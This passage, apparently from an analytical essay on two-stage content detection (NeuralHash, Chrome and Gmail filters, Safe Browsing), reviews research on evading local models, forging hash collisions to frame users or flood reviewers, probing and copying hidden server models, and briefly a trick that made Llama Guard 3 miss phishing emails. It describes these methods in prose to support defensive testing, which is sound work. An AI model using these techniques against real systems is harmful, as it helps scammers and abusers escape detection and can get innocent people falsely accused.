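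To measure false negatives, the researchers identified at least 4,629 duplicates or very similar images in CelebA and counted how many shared a hash. The paper gives NeuralHash's miss rate as 64.7%, although its printed counts and formula give 66.3%. Some of these misses are what Apple would have wanted, because it designed NeuralHash to recognise altered copies of one photo, and the set also includes photos in which a person only has a very similar pose.

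In *Apple's CSAM detection technology*, a review that Apple published with its design, Forsyth (2021) called the false negative rate "moderate" without giving a number, and wrote that the system was nearly certain to catch anyone storing many known images. Both claims can be true even at the rate measured on CelebA. If NeuralHash recognised only 35% of listed images, an account would need about 88 of them to reach 31 matches on average, and one with 200 would almost certainly pass the threshold. An account with 30 or fewer listed images would never be found at any recall, unless duplicates added to its count.

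### What a second hash would repair

A second hash on the server could remove many accidental matches, because another function may give quite different hashes to two portraits that happen to share a NeuralHash. Here too, the useful figure is how often the second hash wrongly confirms flagged images, meaning those that have already matched in NeuralHash.

Rescorla, on Educated Guesswork, points out that a second hash would be worthless if Apple computed it by applying a cryptographic hash to the NeuralHash value. The two codes would look different, but every pair of images that collided in the first would also collide in the second. He suggests that Apple publish statistics on the overlap between its two functions, which it could do without revealing the secret one.

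NeuralHash uses a neural network and PhotoDNA uses conventional image processing, yet both produced false collisions on faces. Leblanc-Albarel and Preneel don't report whether the same pairs of images collided in both. If the same pairs did collide in both, combining two such functions would remove few of the false matches.

The second hash would also work on low-resolution copies. NeuralHash had far more collisions on heavily blurred faces than on sharp ones, and reduced copies lose fine detail in a similar way. Apple would therefore need to measure the second hash's error rate on the copies the server receives, because the rate on full photos could be too low. If the second hash wrongly confirms one photo in a burst of similar photos, it will probably confirm the others too, so ten confirmations may all result from one mistake.

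A second hash can't recover an image that NeuralHash missed. Catching those images would require a better local hash, or one that accepts near matches and so produces more false matches.

Showing that a second hash works takes many natural collisions. If a second hash were run on the 12 pairs of colliding faces and rejected them all, its true error rate on such pairs could still be as high as 22%, at 95% confidence. Showing with the same confidence that the rate is below 1% would require about 300 pairs, all correctly rejected.

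## Testing how far evading the local model defeats the whole system

A local model may miss only a few per cent of bad items in ordinary traffic, but it can miss a far greater share if attackers have a copy of the model and alter each item until it passes.

The server examines an item only if the local model flags it. An attacker with the weights can run the local model on their own computer and, before releasing an item, make sure it won't be flagged. The item then never reaches the server, so improving the server's check would not stop this attacker.

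Suppose attackers alter enough of the 1,000 bad items in the running example to cut the local model's recall from 95% to 10%.

| Situation | Items sent to the server | Correct verdicts | Mistaken verdicts | Combined recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary traffic | 10,940 | 931 | 100 | 93.1% |
| Altered items, same server | 10,090 | 98 | 100 | 9.8% |
| Altered items, perfect server | 10,090 | 100 | 0 | 10% |

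A perfect server finds only two more bad items than the existing one. With the existing server, about half of the verdicts are now wrong, because the attack removes correct flags and leaves the mistaken ones. The operator would notice confirmed flags falling from 1,031 to 198, but a real drop in phishing would look much the same.

Recall falls this far only if attackers alter almost nine in ten bad items. If they altered one in ten, combined recall would still be about 84%. Many attackers won't alter their content at all. Apruzzese, Conti and Yuan (2022) found in *SpacePhish* that easy, realistic changes to phishing pages reduced detection by only 3–10%, and that some detectors withstood the most realistic attacks. A system can therefore have good average recall and still offer almost no protection against attackers who do alter their content.

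### Tests on image hashes and Chrome's filters

In the best-known test on image hashes, *Adversarial Detection Avoidance Attacks*, Jain, Creţu and de Montjoye (2021) attacked five conventional hashes, including Facebook's PDQ but not NeuralHash. For each hash, they made 10,000 attempts to alter a listed picture so that it looked much the same but no longer matched. Every attempt succeeded except for one image with one of the hashes. The method only needed to compute hashes, so hiding how the function works would not have stopped it.

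Newer hashes are no better without extra defences. *Double Down on Defense* reports that white-box attacks on eight neural-network hashes succeeded 98.6% of the time on average. The attacks succeeded 100% of the time against NeuralHash, which Struppek and colleagues had also evaded in 2021.

In *Cracking Classifiers for Evasion*, Liang, Su and colleagues (2016) studied an early version of Chrome's phishing filter that added up the weights of 2,130 scoring rules. Google had hidden the features behind cryptographic hashes, but the researchers fully recovered 84.8% of the rules. They then altered 100 real phishing pages, and all of them got past the filter. They proposed a deep neural network as a defence, expecting that attackers would be unable to work out which changes to a page would lower its score.

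Google later added a neural network, the visual model, which failed the same kind of test. In *A Good Fishman Knows All the Angles*, Miao, Feng and colleagues (2023) altered 135 phishing pages that the visual model had recognised, and all 135 then evaded it. Preparing each page took 10.7 minutes on average on a computer without a graphics processor. In a test, 23 computer science students correctly identified an altered area on only 34% of the altered pages and wrongly reported alterations on 33% of the originals.

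These tests covered only the local models. In *Evaluating the Robustness of a Production Malware Detection System to Transferable Adversarial Attacks*, Nasr, Fratantonio and colleagues (2025) attacked a complete system, Gmail's scanner for malicious attachments. Both of its stages run on Google's servers, but Google had published the weights of the first, a model that identifies a file's type and sends the file to a suitable scanner. Changing 13 bytes fooled this model in 90% of cases. The researchers then sent a malicious PDF through Gmail to a second account of their own, and it arrived. The file never reached the specialised PDF scanner, so they did not have to evade it.

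That demonstration used a single PDF, chosen because popular antivirus products missed it, and the researchers also had to get around some of Gmail's other filters. Google responded by using a different, secret model in production. Even with 50 changed bytes, a well-resourced attacker succeeded against that model only 20% of the time. A two-stage check can't use this defense because its first stage ships to users.

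Language models can also be easy to evade. *Same Attack, Different Judge* (2026) tested detectors on 100 phishing emails. One simple change made Llama Guard 3, a model built for safety classification, miss 62% of the emails it had previously caught. It had no effect on some general-purpose models and made others miss up to 28% of the emails. The study did not test Gemini Nano as Chrome uses it.

### Rehearsing with Chrome's built-in model

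*The Browser Is Now an AI Runtime*, a report from the security company TrendAI, warns that any HTTPS website can run Chrome's on-device language model as often as it likes without asking the visitor. Chrome's own pages support the main point. Google (2026) announced in May that Chrome 148 gives web developers direct access to the model, Gemini Nano, through the Prompt API.

According to Google's documentation, *The Prompt API* (2025), a page and any frames from the same site can use the model by default, while frames from other sites need the page's permission. The visitor must interact with the page before it can first download the model. The model runs only on desktop computers with enough memory and storage, so a website can't run it for every visitor. The documentation doesn't mention a consent prompt or a rate limit.

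Attackers could already test draft pages against the model on their own computers, so the API mainly saves them work. But the documentation doesn't mention scam detection, and Chrome's scam check may use different instructions or settings, so a page that passes an attacker's test could still fail the real check. Local testing also became less useful in October 2026, when Google moved the analysis for Enhanced Protection users to its servers.

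### Avoiding the check instead of fooling the model

Instead of altering an item, an attacker may be able to keep the model from examining it at all, and a more accurate model doesn't help against that.

| Method | Who can use it | Possible response |
|---|---|---|
| Showing the harmful content after the analysis ends | The page's author | Check again when the page changes |
| Making the analysis fail or run out of time | The page's author | Treat some failures as flags |
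| Cloaking, or showing crawlers a harmless page | The page's author | Collect evidence from the visitor's browser |
| Switching the feature off | The device's owner | Check on the server, if it can read the item |
| Modifying the software | The device's owner | Check on the server, if it can read the item |

Kerns (2026), in *Google reveals how much free space Chrome wants to install local AI models*, reports that Chrome users can disable on-device AI in the browser's settings and that the download needs about 20 GB of free space. Some computers will therefore never have the model. This matters little for scam warnings, because most users want them and Chrome can query the server without the local summary. Avoiding the local check matters more when the device's owner is the suspect, since switching off iCloud Photos takes much less skill than altering each picture to evade detection.

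### Making the local model harder to evade

The simplest response is to loosen the local threshold, but an attacker who knows the new threshold can alter the item further. Jain and colleagues estimated how many harmless images a looser threshold would flag each day on WhatsApp, assuming 4.5 billion shared images and a list of 100,000 entries.

| Hash | Harmless images flagged per day, strictest setting | Loosest setting |
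|---|---|---|
| PDQ | 1 million | 1.6 billion |
| pHash | 2 million | 3.3 billion |
| dHash | 3 million | 796 million |
| pHash with unrounded values | 18 million | 660 million |
| aHash | 175 million | 1.1 billion |

The attack still worked at the loosest settings, although it had to change the images more. A server check could reject most of the flags these settings produce, but it would first have to receive up to 3.3 billion images a day.

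Retraining is more promising. After Miao and colleagues retrained Chrome's visual model on 50 of their altered pages, it detected all of the other 85. Filtering out fine detail before classification restored detection for 92 of the 135 pages. But the researchers had made those pages to fool the original model. An attacker would download the new model and make new pages to fool it, and the researchers expected new attacks.

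*Double Down on Defense* tested its defence against attackers who knew about it. The defence compares many slightly noisy versions of two images and makes small changes to the reference image before publication. Together, these steps cut the average success rate of white-box attacks from 98.6% to 11.8%, and the rate against NeuralHash from 100% to 20.6%.

This could work for a photographer protecting new pictures, but nobody can alter abuse images already in circulation. With the noisy comparisons alone, attackers still succeeded 43.8% of the time on average. The comparisons also require the reference image itself, which Apple's phones would not have had. With the full defence, NeuralHash missed 7.7% of copies with ordinary edits such as cropping and compression, compared with none before.

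### Sampling items that the local model passed

If the device also sends the server a random sample of unflagged items, an attacker whose page passes the local model can no longer be sure it will stay hidden from the server. If browsers send 1% of unflagged page visits, a phishing page with 300 visits has about a 95% chance (1 − 0.99³⁰⁰) of at least one sampled visit. The attacker can't improve those odds by testing offline, because each visitor's browser randomly selects which visits to send. If the server recognises the page as phishing, it can protect later visitors.

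The early visitors remain exposed because the first sample comes, on average, on the hundredth visit. A page with only 20 visits has an 18% chance of being sampled at all. Chrome's rate of one in a million is far too low for this purpose. At that rate, the page with 300 visits would have a 0.03% chance of being sampled, and a page would need about three million visits to reach 95%.

The sample has to include what the browser displayed. If it contains only the address, the server must fetch the page itself and may receive a harmless version. The server also needs to group related addresses, since a scammer can give each victim a different link.

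In the running example, sampling 1% of unflagged items would send the server about 9,900 more items, nearly doubling its work. Only nine of those would be among the 900 bad items that the local model missed. If the server wrongly confirmed 1% of the harmless ones, that would add about 99 false positives. Sampling can still be worthwhile for public web pages, because one detection can protect hundreds of people who visit the same page.

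Private photos rarely offer that benefit. A 1% sample would expose about 100 pictures from a library of 10,000, and nearly all the people affected would be innocent. If someone had 20 altered abuse images, the chance of sampling at least one would be only 18%. If the system also required 30 matches, that person would need about 3,000 altered images on average to reach the threshold.

Finding one altered photo also does little to help find others. When Jain and colleagues made 50 altered versions of each of 100 pictures, the hashes of a picture's versions typically differed from one another by about the match threshold, so adding some of them to the list would not reliably catch the rest. The owner of a modified phone could also withhold any photo selected for the sample. These problems would make sampling private photos hard to justify even if it didn't break Apple's promise not to look at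 photos that don't match.

### Finding bad items without a local flag

Crawlers and user reports can find a phishing page whatever score the local model gives it. But *TraceScope* (2026) describes sites that inspect the visitor's browser, block IP addresses belonging to data centres, or show the login form only after the visitor solves a puzzle. TraceScope is an automated investigator that operates a browser to reveal such hidden behaviour. It isn't designed to filter all web traffic, so it examines individual URLs after a prompt such as a user report.

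User reports avoid the cloaking problem because they come from people who saw the real page, but they arrive late, and only if someone recognises the scam. If a photo stays in one person's library, there may be nobody to report it.

*Client-Side Zero-Shot LLM Inference for Comprehensive In-Browser URL Analysis* (2025) instead recommends running the analysis in the visitor's own browser, where a cloaked site is more likely to show its real content. This also keeps the address private, but it gives attackers access to the model again. A better approach is for the server to request a report from the visitor's browser when an address already looks suspicious, as Chrome's servers can.

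The operator could also send every item to the server. In the running example, this would raise recall to 98% even if the local model missed nearly everything. But the server would have to examine a million items, about 90 times as many as before the attack. If its false positive rate stayed at 1%, it would produce 9,990 false positives and only 980 true positives, so the operator would need a much stricter server. Users would lose the privacy that justified the local model, and a service with end-to-end encryption could not send every item without giving the operator access to everyone's messages. Google's 2026 design for scam pages is a compromise in which Chrome sends a page's text only if the page shows certain indicators.

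### A test with the server on and off

An operator can measure how much protection remains by giving a team of testers the same advantages as a white-box attacker.

1. Collect current bad items and record the local model's recall on them. For an abuse-image system, use harmless pictures on a separate test list, since the hash works the same way whatever the pictures show.
2. Give the testers everything that ships to users, including weights, thresholds and allowlists, and explain any defences. Don't give them access to the server.
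3. Have them alter each item until the local model stops flagging it or they reach a set time limit. The altered item must still do its job, so a phishing page must still deceive people and a picture must remain recognisable.
4. Run the original and altered items with the server off, counting every flag as a verdict. Then run them again with the server confirming or rejecting each flag.
5. Turn on the methods that don't need a local flag, such as random sampling and server requests, one at a time. Record how many altered items each one finds.
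6. Repeat the attack from step 2 whenever the model or a defence changes. Reusing the old altered items would make a retrained model look stronger than it is.

In the running example, step 4 would give a recall of 95% on the original items with the server off and 93.1% with it on. On the altered items, recall would be 10% with the server off and 9.8% with it on. Only the methods in step 5 could raise the last figure above 10%. Attempts to avoid the check, for instance by delaying the harmful content, need a separate test because they may succeed even if the model still flags every altered item.

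The operator should also record how much work each evasion took. *Robustness, Cost, and Attack-Surface Concentration in Phishing Detection* (2026) assigns a cost to each change an attacker can make and looks for the lowest-cost combination that gets a phishing page past the detector. Its attackers don't have the model's weights, but the same measure is useful when they do. A defence that increases the work per page from ten minutes to a week may deter most scammers, even if a determined one still succeeds every time.

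Testers should try several methods, because attacks that use knowledge of how a model works aren't always the most effective. In one experiment by Jain and colleagues, two attacks based on the mathematics of the hash succeeded on 98.4% and 62.2% of images, while the method that only observed the hash's output succeeded on all of them.

The test setup can also produce false results. Chrome doesn't run its phishing models on pages from a private network, so every page on a tester's local server would appear to evade them. Miao and colleagues had to remove this restriction from their copy of the browser before testing. Their sample of 135 pages was large enough that, if every altered page evaded the model, its true recall against that attack on similar pages would probably be no higher than about 2%.

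## Withstanding forced false flags that frame users or flood reviewers

An attacker who can alter a listed image to avoid a match can also alter a harmless one to force a match. The server check is much more useful against forced false flags because they all reach the server, while images that successfully evade the on-device model never do.

Attackers can force false flags either to get a particular person accused (framing) or just to tie up servers or human reviewers (flooding).

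### What each attack needs

The table uses Apple's 2021 design as the example, because it had the most safeguards.

| Requirement | Framing | Flooding reviewers | Safeguard |
|---|---|---|---|
| The local model | Yes | Yes | None, because it ships on every phone |
| A hash that is on the list | Yes | Yes | The encrypted list, though anyone with a listed image can compute its hash |
| Delivery | The victim must keep the images and upload them | The attacker can use their own accounts | None |
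| Enough matches | More than 30 in one library | More than 30 in each account | The match threshold |
| Agreement of the server check | Yes | Yes, or no person sees the images | The second hash |
| Agreement of a reviewer | Yes | No | Human review |

Framing a user is harder than flooding reviewers because the attack has to succeed at every stage. The victim has to save more than 30 of the attacker's pictures, which is unlikely if they choose what to save but more likely if a messaging app saves everything it receives. An attacker who wants to flood reviewers doesn't have to send pictures to a victim, and may not need forged images, since a modified phone could report matches that don't exist.

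### Forging NeuralHash matches

In August 2021, someone using the name Asuhariet Ygvar published a tool that converts Apple's NeuralHash into a standard format. Cory Cornelius used it to make two different images with the same hash. 9to5Mac's *Apple CSAM system tricked, but easy to guard against* reports that this took only hours. Apple replied that the extracted version was generic, not final, and that it had never meant the algorithm to be secret. But the final version would also have run on phones, where attackers could have extracted it the same way.

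Struppek and colleagues then measured how reliably the attack works. They used 20,580 photos of dogs as a stand-in for the abuse list and tried to forge matches from 10,000 other pictures. For each picture, they chose the listed hash closest to its own and altered the picture in small steps to try to make the two hashes equal. They succeeded with 90.81% of the pictures, after an average of 1,190 steps. Most of the altered pictures had patches of colour, which were sometimes conspicuous but often hard to notice.

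In the test, the attacker had the whole list and could aim each picture at the nearest of 20,580 hashes. Apple's list was encrypted, and a framer who knew only a few of its hashes would often have to change a picture more. The forged matches may also be fragile. The researchers stopped altering each picture as soon as the hashes agreed, and NeuralHash requires all 96 digits to be equal. In a separate test, JPEG compression that kept reasonable quality changed about 2% of the digits in an ordinary picture's hash, or about two of the 96. A forged picture might therefore no longer match if a messaging app recompresses it on its way to the victim. The paper notes that a more demanding version of the attack could make the match more likely to survive such changes.

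Struppek and colleagues suggest that a second hash on the server, unavailable to attackers, would make forged matches less effective. But they object that the operator would then need to be able to read users' images. Apple's design partly addresses this objection, since its servers could open only reduced copies of matching photos, and only after the account passed the threshold.

### Forging matches on older hashes

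An attacker can't directly calculate which changes will bring an image's hash closer to a target with Microsoft's PhotoDNA or Facebook's PDQ, as they can with NeuralHash. Prokos, Fendley and colleagues (2023) got around this in *Squint Hard Enough* by making many small random changes and observing which ones reduced the distance to the target hash.

The researchers tried 30 randomly chosen pairs of images. With PDQ, all 30 attempts produced a match, although the closest matches had heavy visible noise. For PhotoDNA, the paper's main account reports 17 successes out of 30, but its comparison of different versions of the attack reports success rates of 83% to 90%. The paper doesn't explain the difference. Each PhotoDNA run took about four hours, though the researchers expected better code to be faster. They had to choose their own limit for how close two PhotoDNA hashes must be to count as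 a match.

In *White-Box Attacks on PhotoDNA Perceptual Hash Function*, Deryck, Leblanc-Albarel and Preneel (2026) describe a function that gives the same outputs as PhotoDNA on a large dataset. They conclude that it is easy to incriminate someone by sending them an image whose hash is close to that of illegal content. Choosing PhotoDNA for the second stage is therefore not enough to keep that stage secret.

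Prokos and colleagues also describe framing in the opposite direction, where the attacker alters an illegal-looking image until its hash matches that of the victim's unaltered, harmless picture. The attacker then gets the altered image onto the list, perhaps by leaving it where the list's curators will find it. From then on, anyone who sends the harmless picture triggers a match. The attacker doesn't need to get a picture onto the victim's device, because the target can be one that the victim already has or is sure to share, such as a popular meme.

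Apple's rule that two organisations in different countries must supply each entry would make it harder to plant such an image, but an attacker could try to plant it with both. A second hash could still reject the match because the listed image and the harmless picture look different, so the attacker would have to make them collide in both hashes.

### Identifying people without accusing them

Some attackers only want to know who has a picture. Struppek and colleagues describe a government that alters images popular with its critics so that they match the list, then spreads them on social media. Anyone who saves and uploads enough of them gets flagged. The attacker needs access to the matches, either by controlling the operator or through one of its employees, but doesn't need a reviewer to mistake a protest photo for abuse.

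Human review doesn't prevent this, because the match identifies the person before a reviewer can reject it. Prokos and colleagues argue that this kind of insider is a realistic threat, citing former Twitter employees whom US prosecutors charged in 2019 over alleged spying on critics of Saudi Arabia.

Apple's match threshold gives some protection, since one or two of the altered pictures would not reach it. A system that reports to the operator after a single match lacks that protection. To stop the attack, the server check would have to reject a forged match before anyone at the company could link it to an account.

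### Whether a forged image also fools the server

The early evidence that forged images fail at the second stage came from one pair of pictures. Brad Dwyer, a co-founder of the computer vision company Roboflow, ran Cornelius's two colliding images through CLIP, an OpenAI model that relates images to text, and CLIP told them apart. Dwyer concluded, in comments that 9to5Mac reprinted, that Apple could use a similar network as its second check and that fooling both checks would be much harder.

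The test shows that two images that collide in one network don't always collide in another. But nobody had designed the pair to fool CLIP, and one pair isn't enough to estimate how often a collision would carry over. Dwyer was more cautious in a second post on Roboflow the next day. Forged images had already improved, and he wrote that it was unclear how hard it would be to make one that fooled NeuralHash, the server's model and the reviewers together.

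Two later measurements of transfer, meaning an attack's success on a model the attacker hasn't seen, gave very different results. In one, Prokos and colleagues trained neural networks to imitate PhotoDNA and PDQ, then forged images against the imitations. None of the forged images matched under the real functions. They attribute this to the imitations, which fitted the real hashes poorly, so the result is weak evidence about whether attacks transfer between models that do resemble each other.

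By contrast, *Clean Image May be Dangerous* (2025) found success rates above 60% in most of its tests of attacks built for one neural-network hashing method and tried on another. The attack plants altered images in an image search system's training data, so the figure isn't a rate of forged matches. It is still a reason not to pair two neural-network hashes on the assumption that an attack on one will fail on the other.

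None of these studies ran a large set of images forged against NeuralHash through a second hash. An operator can run this kind of test privately with its own two models. As with accidental collisions, the hidden model would need to reject all of about 300 forged images to show that it probably accepts fewer than 1% of such images. The test should include images made to fool both the local model and well-known public models, because the hidden model may resemble one of the public ones.

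Rescorla, on Educated Guesswork, guessed that Apple's second hash was structured like NeuralHash but used different features. A second check would be safer if it differed more from the first, for example by using another type of model or, better still, information that the attacker can't alter by editing the item.

### Starting from an image that resembles the target

Transfer rates also depend on the picture the attacker starts with. Dwyer's test used two images that looked nothing alike, which makes the second model's task easy. An attacker can instead choose a harmless picture that resembles the listed one in pose, background and lighting. Both hashes are then likely to be closer to their targets before the attacker changes anything.

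Leblanc-Albarel and Preneel found accidental collisions between faces in both NeuralHash and PhotoDNA, which supports this concern. If a listed image shows a face, a forger would probably do better to start from a portrait than from a landscape.

A classifier on the server has a similar weakness. It detects a category of content rather than one particular image, so the attacker only needs a picture near the edge of that category. Legal adult pornography is the obvious choice against a system that detects abuse images, and it might also mislead a reviewer.

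Someone trying to frame a user can't start with an image too close to the target, because the victim is unlikely to keep a picture that looks like child abuse. Someone flooding reviewers has no such limit, since the images only have to sit in the flooder's own accounts. Tests of the server check should therefore include forgeries that start close to the target, because testing only random pictures would underestimate how often forgeries that fool the on-device model also fool the server check.

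### How many matches the server should confirm

How well a second hash protects against framing depends heavily on how many of an account's matches it must confirm before reviewers see them, which Apple did not specify. Suppose a framer gets exactly 31 forged images into a library, and each has the same independent chance of fooling the server. The table gives the probability that the account reaches the reviewers.

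| Confirmations required | 1% transfer | 20% transfer | 60% transfer |
|---|---|---|---|
| At least 1 of 31 | 27% | 99.9% | Almost 100% |
| At least 10 of 31 | Under 1 in a trillion | 7.5% | Over 99.9% |
| At least 16 of 31 | Under 1 in a trillion | About 1 in 11,000 | 87% |

If a single confirmation is enough, even a good server check gives little protection against 31 attempts. Requiring 16 confirmations almost eliminates the risk at a transfer rate of 20%. It also barely reduces detection, because with the server's 98% recall from the running example, an account with 31 genuine matches would almost certainly still reach 16 confirmations.

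The framer can respond by planting more images. At 20% transfer, 80 images would produce 16 confirmations on average, but the victim would have to keep all 80. The calculation also assumes that one success doesn't make another more likely. If the framer finds a type of picture that fools both models, most of the 31 could be confirmed. At 60% transfer, no reasonable confirmation threshold helps much, so the operator needs a server model that differs more from the local one.

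### The load on servers and reviewers

In the running example, the local model flags 10,940 of a million items and the server confirms 1,031 of them. Suppose a flooder adds 100,000 forged items and the local model flags them all. The server now has 110,940 items to check, about ten times as many as before. If it wrongly confirms 1% of the forged items, it adds 1,000 false confirmations. If it wrongly confirms 20%, it adds 20,000.

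The next table assumes that a person reviews every confirmed item and takes two minutes over each.

| Share of forged items that fool the server | Items for review | Reviewer hours | Share of reviewed items that are bad |
|---|---|---|---|
| No attack | 1,031 | 34 | 90% |
| 1% | 2,031 | 68 | 46% |
| 20% | 21,031 | 701 | 4.4% |
| 60% | 61,031 | 2,034 | 1.5% |

Without a server check, reviewers would spend about 3,700 hours looking at all 110,940 items, so even a mediocre check saves a lot of work. The 20% rate is a guess for image forgery, but it matches the rate at which Nasr and colleagues' strongest attacker evaded Google's secret file-type model.

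How much 701 hours of work matters depends on the size of the team. Abelson and colleagues note that Facebook alone had 15,000 human moderators. If all of them were available, they could do that work in minutes. But suppose a specialist team has eight reviewers who each spend six hours a day on cases, and the million items are one day's traffic. The team has 48 hours of capacity a day and normally uses 34. After a one-day flood with 20% transfer, it would need nearly seven weeks to clear the backlog. Genuine cases would wait in the same queue unless the operator could pick them out.

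In Apple's design, a flood of forged images would add less work for the servers, because phones send an encrypted record for every photo whether it matches or not. The match threshold would also force the attacker to spread the images over many accounts. With 31 in each, 100,000 images would fill about 3,225 accounts. Suppose each forged image had a 20% chance of also fooling the server's check. Nearly all the accounts would then reach reviewers if one confirmed image were enough, but probably none would if the server had to confirm 16 per account.

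Nicholas Weaver, a security researcher at the International Computer Science Institute, thought forged matches could only annoy Apple's reviewers. He expected Apple to respond by filtering out the junk images. Rescorla agreed that human review would probably prevent most false reports to the police, but doubted it would work well if there were very many cases.

### Flooding Safe Browsing with colliding addresses

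In Google Safe Browsing, an attacker can force extra server checks without being able to frame a harmless page. The attacker can find a malicious address whose hash starts with the same four bytes as that of a popular harmless page. Once Google lists the malicious address, every browser with the updated list flags the harmless page and checks it with the server, but shows no warning because the full hashes differ. To frame the page, the attacker would have to match all 32 bytes of its hash, which nobody knows how to do.

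The extra requests can still burden Google. In *On the (In)security of Google Safe Browsing*, Gerbet, Kumar and Lauradoux searched for colliding addresses for a million popular sites and found over 111 million, about 100 per site, in one week on a 32-core machine. If even one of these addresses were listed, every visit to the target page would cause a request, unless the browser had already stored the server's answer.

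An attacker can also make the server's replies larger. If Google listed 100 malicious addresses with the same hash prefix, its server would have to return all 100 full hashes to anyone who visited the harmless page. The researchers calculated that the reply to a 21-byte request would grow from about 315 bytes to 30 kilobytes. They acknowledged that the attacker depends on Google to find the addresses and list them separately. Google might instead list the whole malicious site under one hash, which would remove most of the collisions.

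Longer prefixes would make collisions much harder to find, but 64-bit prefixes would have tripled the size of the local list in 2015. The researchers also proposed mixing a secret key into each prefix. If every user had a different key, a collision would affect only one person, but Google would have to compute a separate list for each user. A shared key that changed every week or month would be easier to manage, but every browser would have to download the whole list again each time the key changed.

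Chrome's real-time checks have reduced the effect of this attack, because the browser already checks most unfamiliar addresses with the server. The attack still matters for browsers that rely on a local list, such as Firefox. It could also affect popular sites in Chrome's Global Cache, because Chrome still checks those against local threat lists.

### Reducing the damage

An operator can limit how many flags from one account the server or reviewers will process in a day. With a limit of 50, a flooder would need 2,000 accounts to get 100,000 items processed in a day. The limit works best if accounts are hard to create in bulk, such as when each one requires a verified phone number. The operator should delay or sample flags above the limit instead of deleting them, because otherwise someone could use up an account's daily allowance with forged items to hide a real one.

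Grouping near-identical flags saves reviewers from judging the same picture repeatedly. If the 20,000 forged items that fooled the server were copies of 200 pictures, reviewers could check them in under seven hours instead of 667. A flooder can defeat grouping by making every picture different, but that takes computing time. At the four hours per run that Prokos and colleagues needed for PhotoDNA, 100,000 different pictures would take one machine about 46 years. Forging NeuralHash matches is probably much faster, so grouping would be less effective in a system that uses NeuralHash.

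A reviewer's decision should apply only to items whose visible content is nearly identical, as judged by a comparison that doesn't rely on the local hash. If reviewers rejected a forged image and the system then dismissed everything with the same NeuralHash, it would also dismiss the real abuse image whose hash the attacker copied. An attacker could then use a flood of forgeries to evade detection. Weaver's filter for junk images would carry the same risk if it were too broad.

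Automatic rejection should come before human review and, where the design allows it, before a match counts towards the threshold. The operator can also have reviewers start with the accounts that have the highest share of confirmed matches. They should then see genuine collections before most forged ones, as long as the transfer rate is low. A model that detects the coloured patches typical of forged images could also help, but attackers would learn to avoid producing those patches.

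No account should lose access because of an unreviewed flag, even when reviewers are weeks behind. Leblanc-Albarel and Preneel point out that people can lose their data and reputation while they wait for an appeal, even if the company later restores the account. Prokos and colleagues report that providers often keep a user banned even after the police have found that the match was false.

Reviewers could also recognise framing more easily if they saw when the matches arrived. If 31 matches appear within an hour in a library that had none before, someone may have planted them. Moving an existing collection to a new account would produce the same pattern, so the timing is a reason to look more closely at the images but not enough to clear the account.

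## Deciding what the device learns about the server's verdict

A forged image is more useful to an attacker who can find out whether the server misclassified it. If the system reacts visibly to the server's verdict, the attacker learns something about the hidden model from each reaction. With enough reactions, an attacker can get an item past the model or build an approximate copy of it.

Evaders need the server's answers only if the server also checks items that the local model passed, for instance because of a suspicious web address. Framers benefit more from probing the server, since the local model must flag their forgeries and the server must then confirm them.

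### How many answers an attack needs

Suppose the server gives a page a score of 0.80 and confirms flags when the score is above 0.50. An attacker who can see the score can change the page one part at a time, keeping a change that lowers the score to 0.78 and undoing one that raises it to 0.83.

If the attacker sees only yes or no, two changes that get the same answer don't show which one helped. The attacker first has to find the boundary where the answer changes. With pictures, they can blend a bad image with a harmless one and keep halving the range between a blend that the server confirms and one that it doesn't. Ten halvings locate the boundary to within about a thousandth of the range. The attacker then tests small changes near the boundary, looking for a version that is closer to the original bad image but that the server still doesn't confirm.

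Most measurements of these attacks use image classifiers. *Query-Efficient Hard-label Black-box Attack* (2018) tested early methods that use only yes-or-no answers, and *Evading Black-box Classifiers Without Breaking Eggs* (Debenedetti, Carlini and Tramèr, 2023) compared later ones. *Hard-label based Small Query Black-box Adversarial Attack* (Park, Miller and McLaughlin, 2024) let the attacker use a similar model to choose each try. The figure for scores comes from *Blacklight* (2020), which proposes a defence against probing.

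| What the attacker sees | Approximate queries per image | Source |
|---|---|---|
| A score | Often thousands in 2020 | *Blacklight* |
| Yes or no, early methods | 71,000 to 261,000 | *Query-Efficient Hard-label Black-box Attack* |
| Yes or no, later methods | 330 to 9,700 | Debenedetti and colleagues |
| Yes or no, guided by a similar model | Some successes within 100 to 250 | Park and colleagues |
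| Yes or no, after a delay | The same number, spread over more time | |
| Nothing | None, because the attack has to rely on transfer | |

The rows come from different tests, so they don't show that scores are less useful than yes-or-no answers. An attacker who sees a score can always turn it into a yes-or-no answer by checking which side of the threshold it is on. A score with two decimal places can carry up to 6.7 bits of information, compared with at most one bit for a yes-or-no answer.

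The number of queries an attack needs also varies from image to image. *BlackboxBench* (2023), a comparison of many attacks, counted a yes-or-no attack as a failure if it had not succeeded after 10,000 queries. Some images resisted every method or took a very large number of queries, and these tended to be far from the model's decision boundary.

Park and colleagues' result matters most for a two-stage check. Their attack, guided by a model similar to the target, succeeded about five times as often as the methods they compared it with, especially at 100 and 250 queries. An attacker who has the on-device model may already have such a guide, because the operator probably trained it for much the same task as the server's model.

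### Copying the hidden model

An attacker can also use the server's answers to train a copy of its model, then attack the copy offline. In *Explore the vulnerability of black-box models via diffusion models* (2025), the attacker used generated images as queries and saw the target model's scores. After 5,000 queries, the copy correctly classified 88.8% of a set of small images, compared with 93.9% for the original. On a task with 100 categories, the copy was 72.3% accurate after 150,000 queries, compared with 79.9% for the original. Copies trained on yes-or-no answers were less accurate.

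*End-to-End Hard-Label Cryptanalytic Model Extraction Using Efficient Sign Recovery* (2026) describes a more ambitious attack, which tries to recover a model's parameters using only the categories it returns. The attacker must already know how many layers and units the model has, which an operator can keep secret. Even with a perfect copy of a model that analyzes web pages, an attacker would lack the other evidence Google's servers use, such as a site's reputation.

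To train a copy of the server's model, the attacker needs examples from both sides of its decision boundary, so they have to submit some items that the server will confirm as bad. In a two-stage check, they can use the local model to choose items that will reach the server and avoid spending queries on the rest.

### Attacking image search without repeated queries

Hao, Luo and colleagues (2021) tested both probing and transfer on perceptual hashes in *It's Not What It Looks Like*. In the laboratory, their attacker could submit an image and receive its full hash, which reveals far more than a verdict. The attack took an average of about 89 rounds of changes, each with several queries, to alter 20 of the 64 digits in a pHash code.

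The researchers tested the commercial image search engines without probing them this way. They altered pictures to defeat a hash running on their own computer, then submitted the finished pictures to TinEye, Google, Bing and Yandex. After a trial with five pictures, they chose the best method, strengthened it and tried it on 50 more.

| Search engine | Searches with a correct match in the top ten, original picture | Altered picture |
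|---|---|---|
| TinEye | 100% | 0% |
| Google | 96% | 36% |
| Yandex | 86% | 58% |
| Bing | 34% | 0% |

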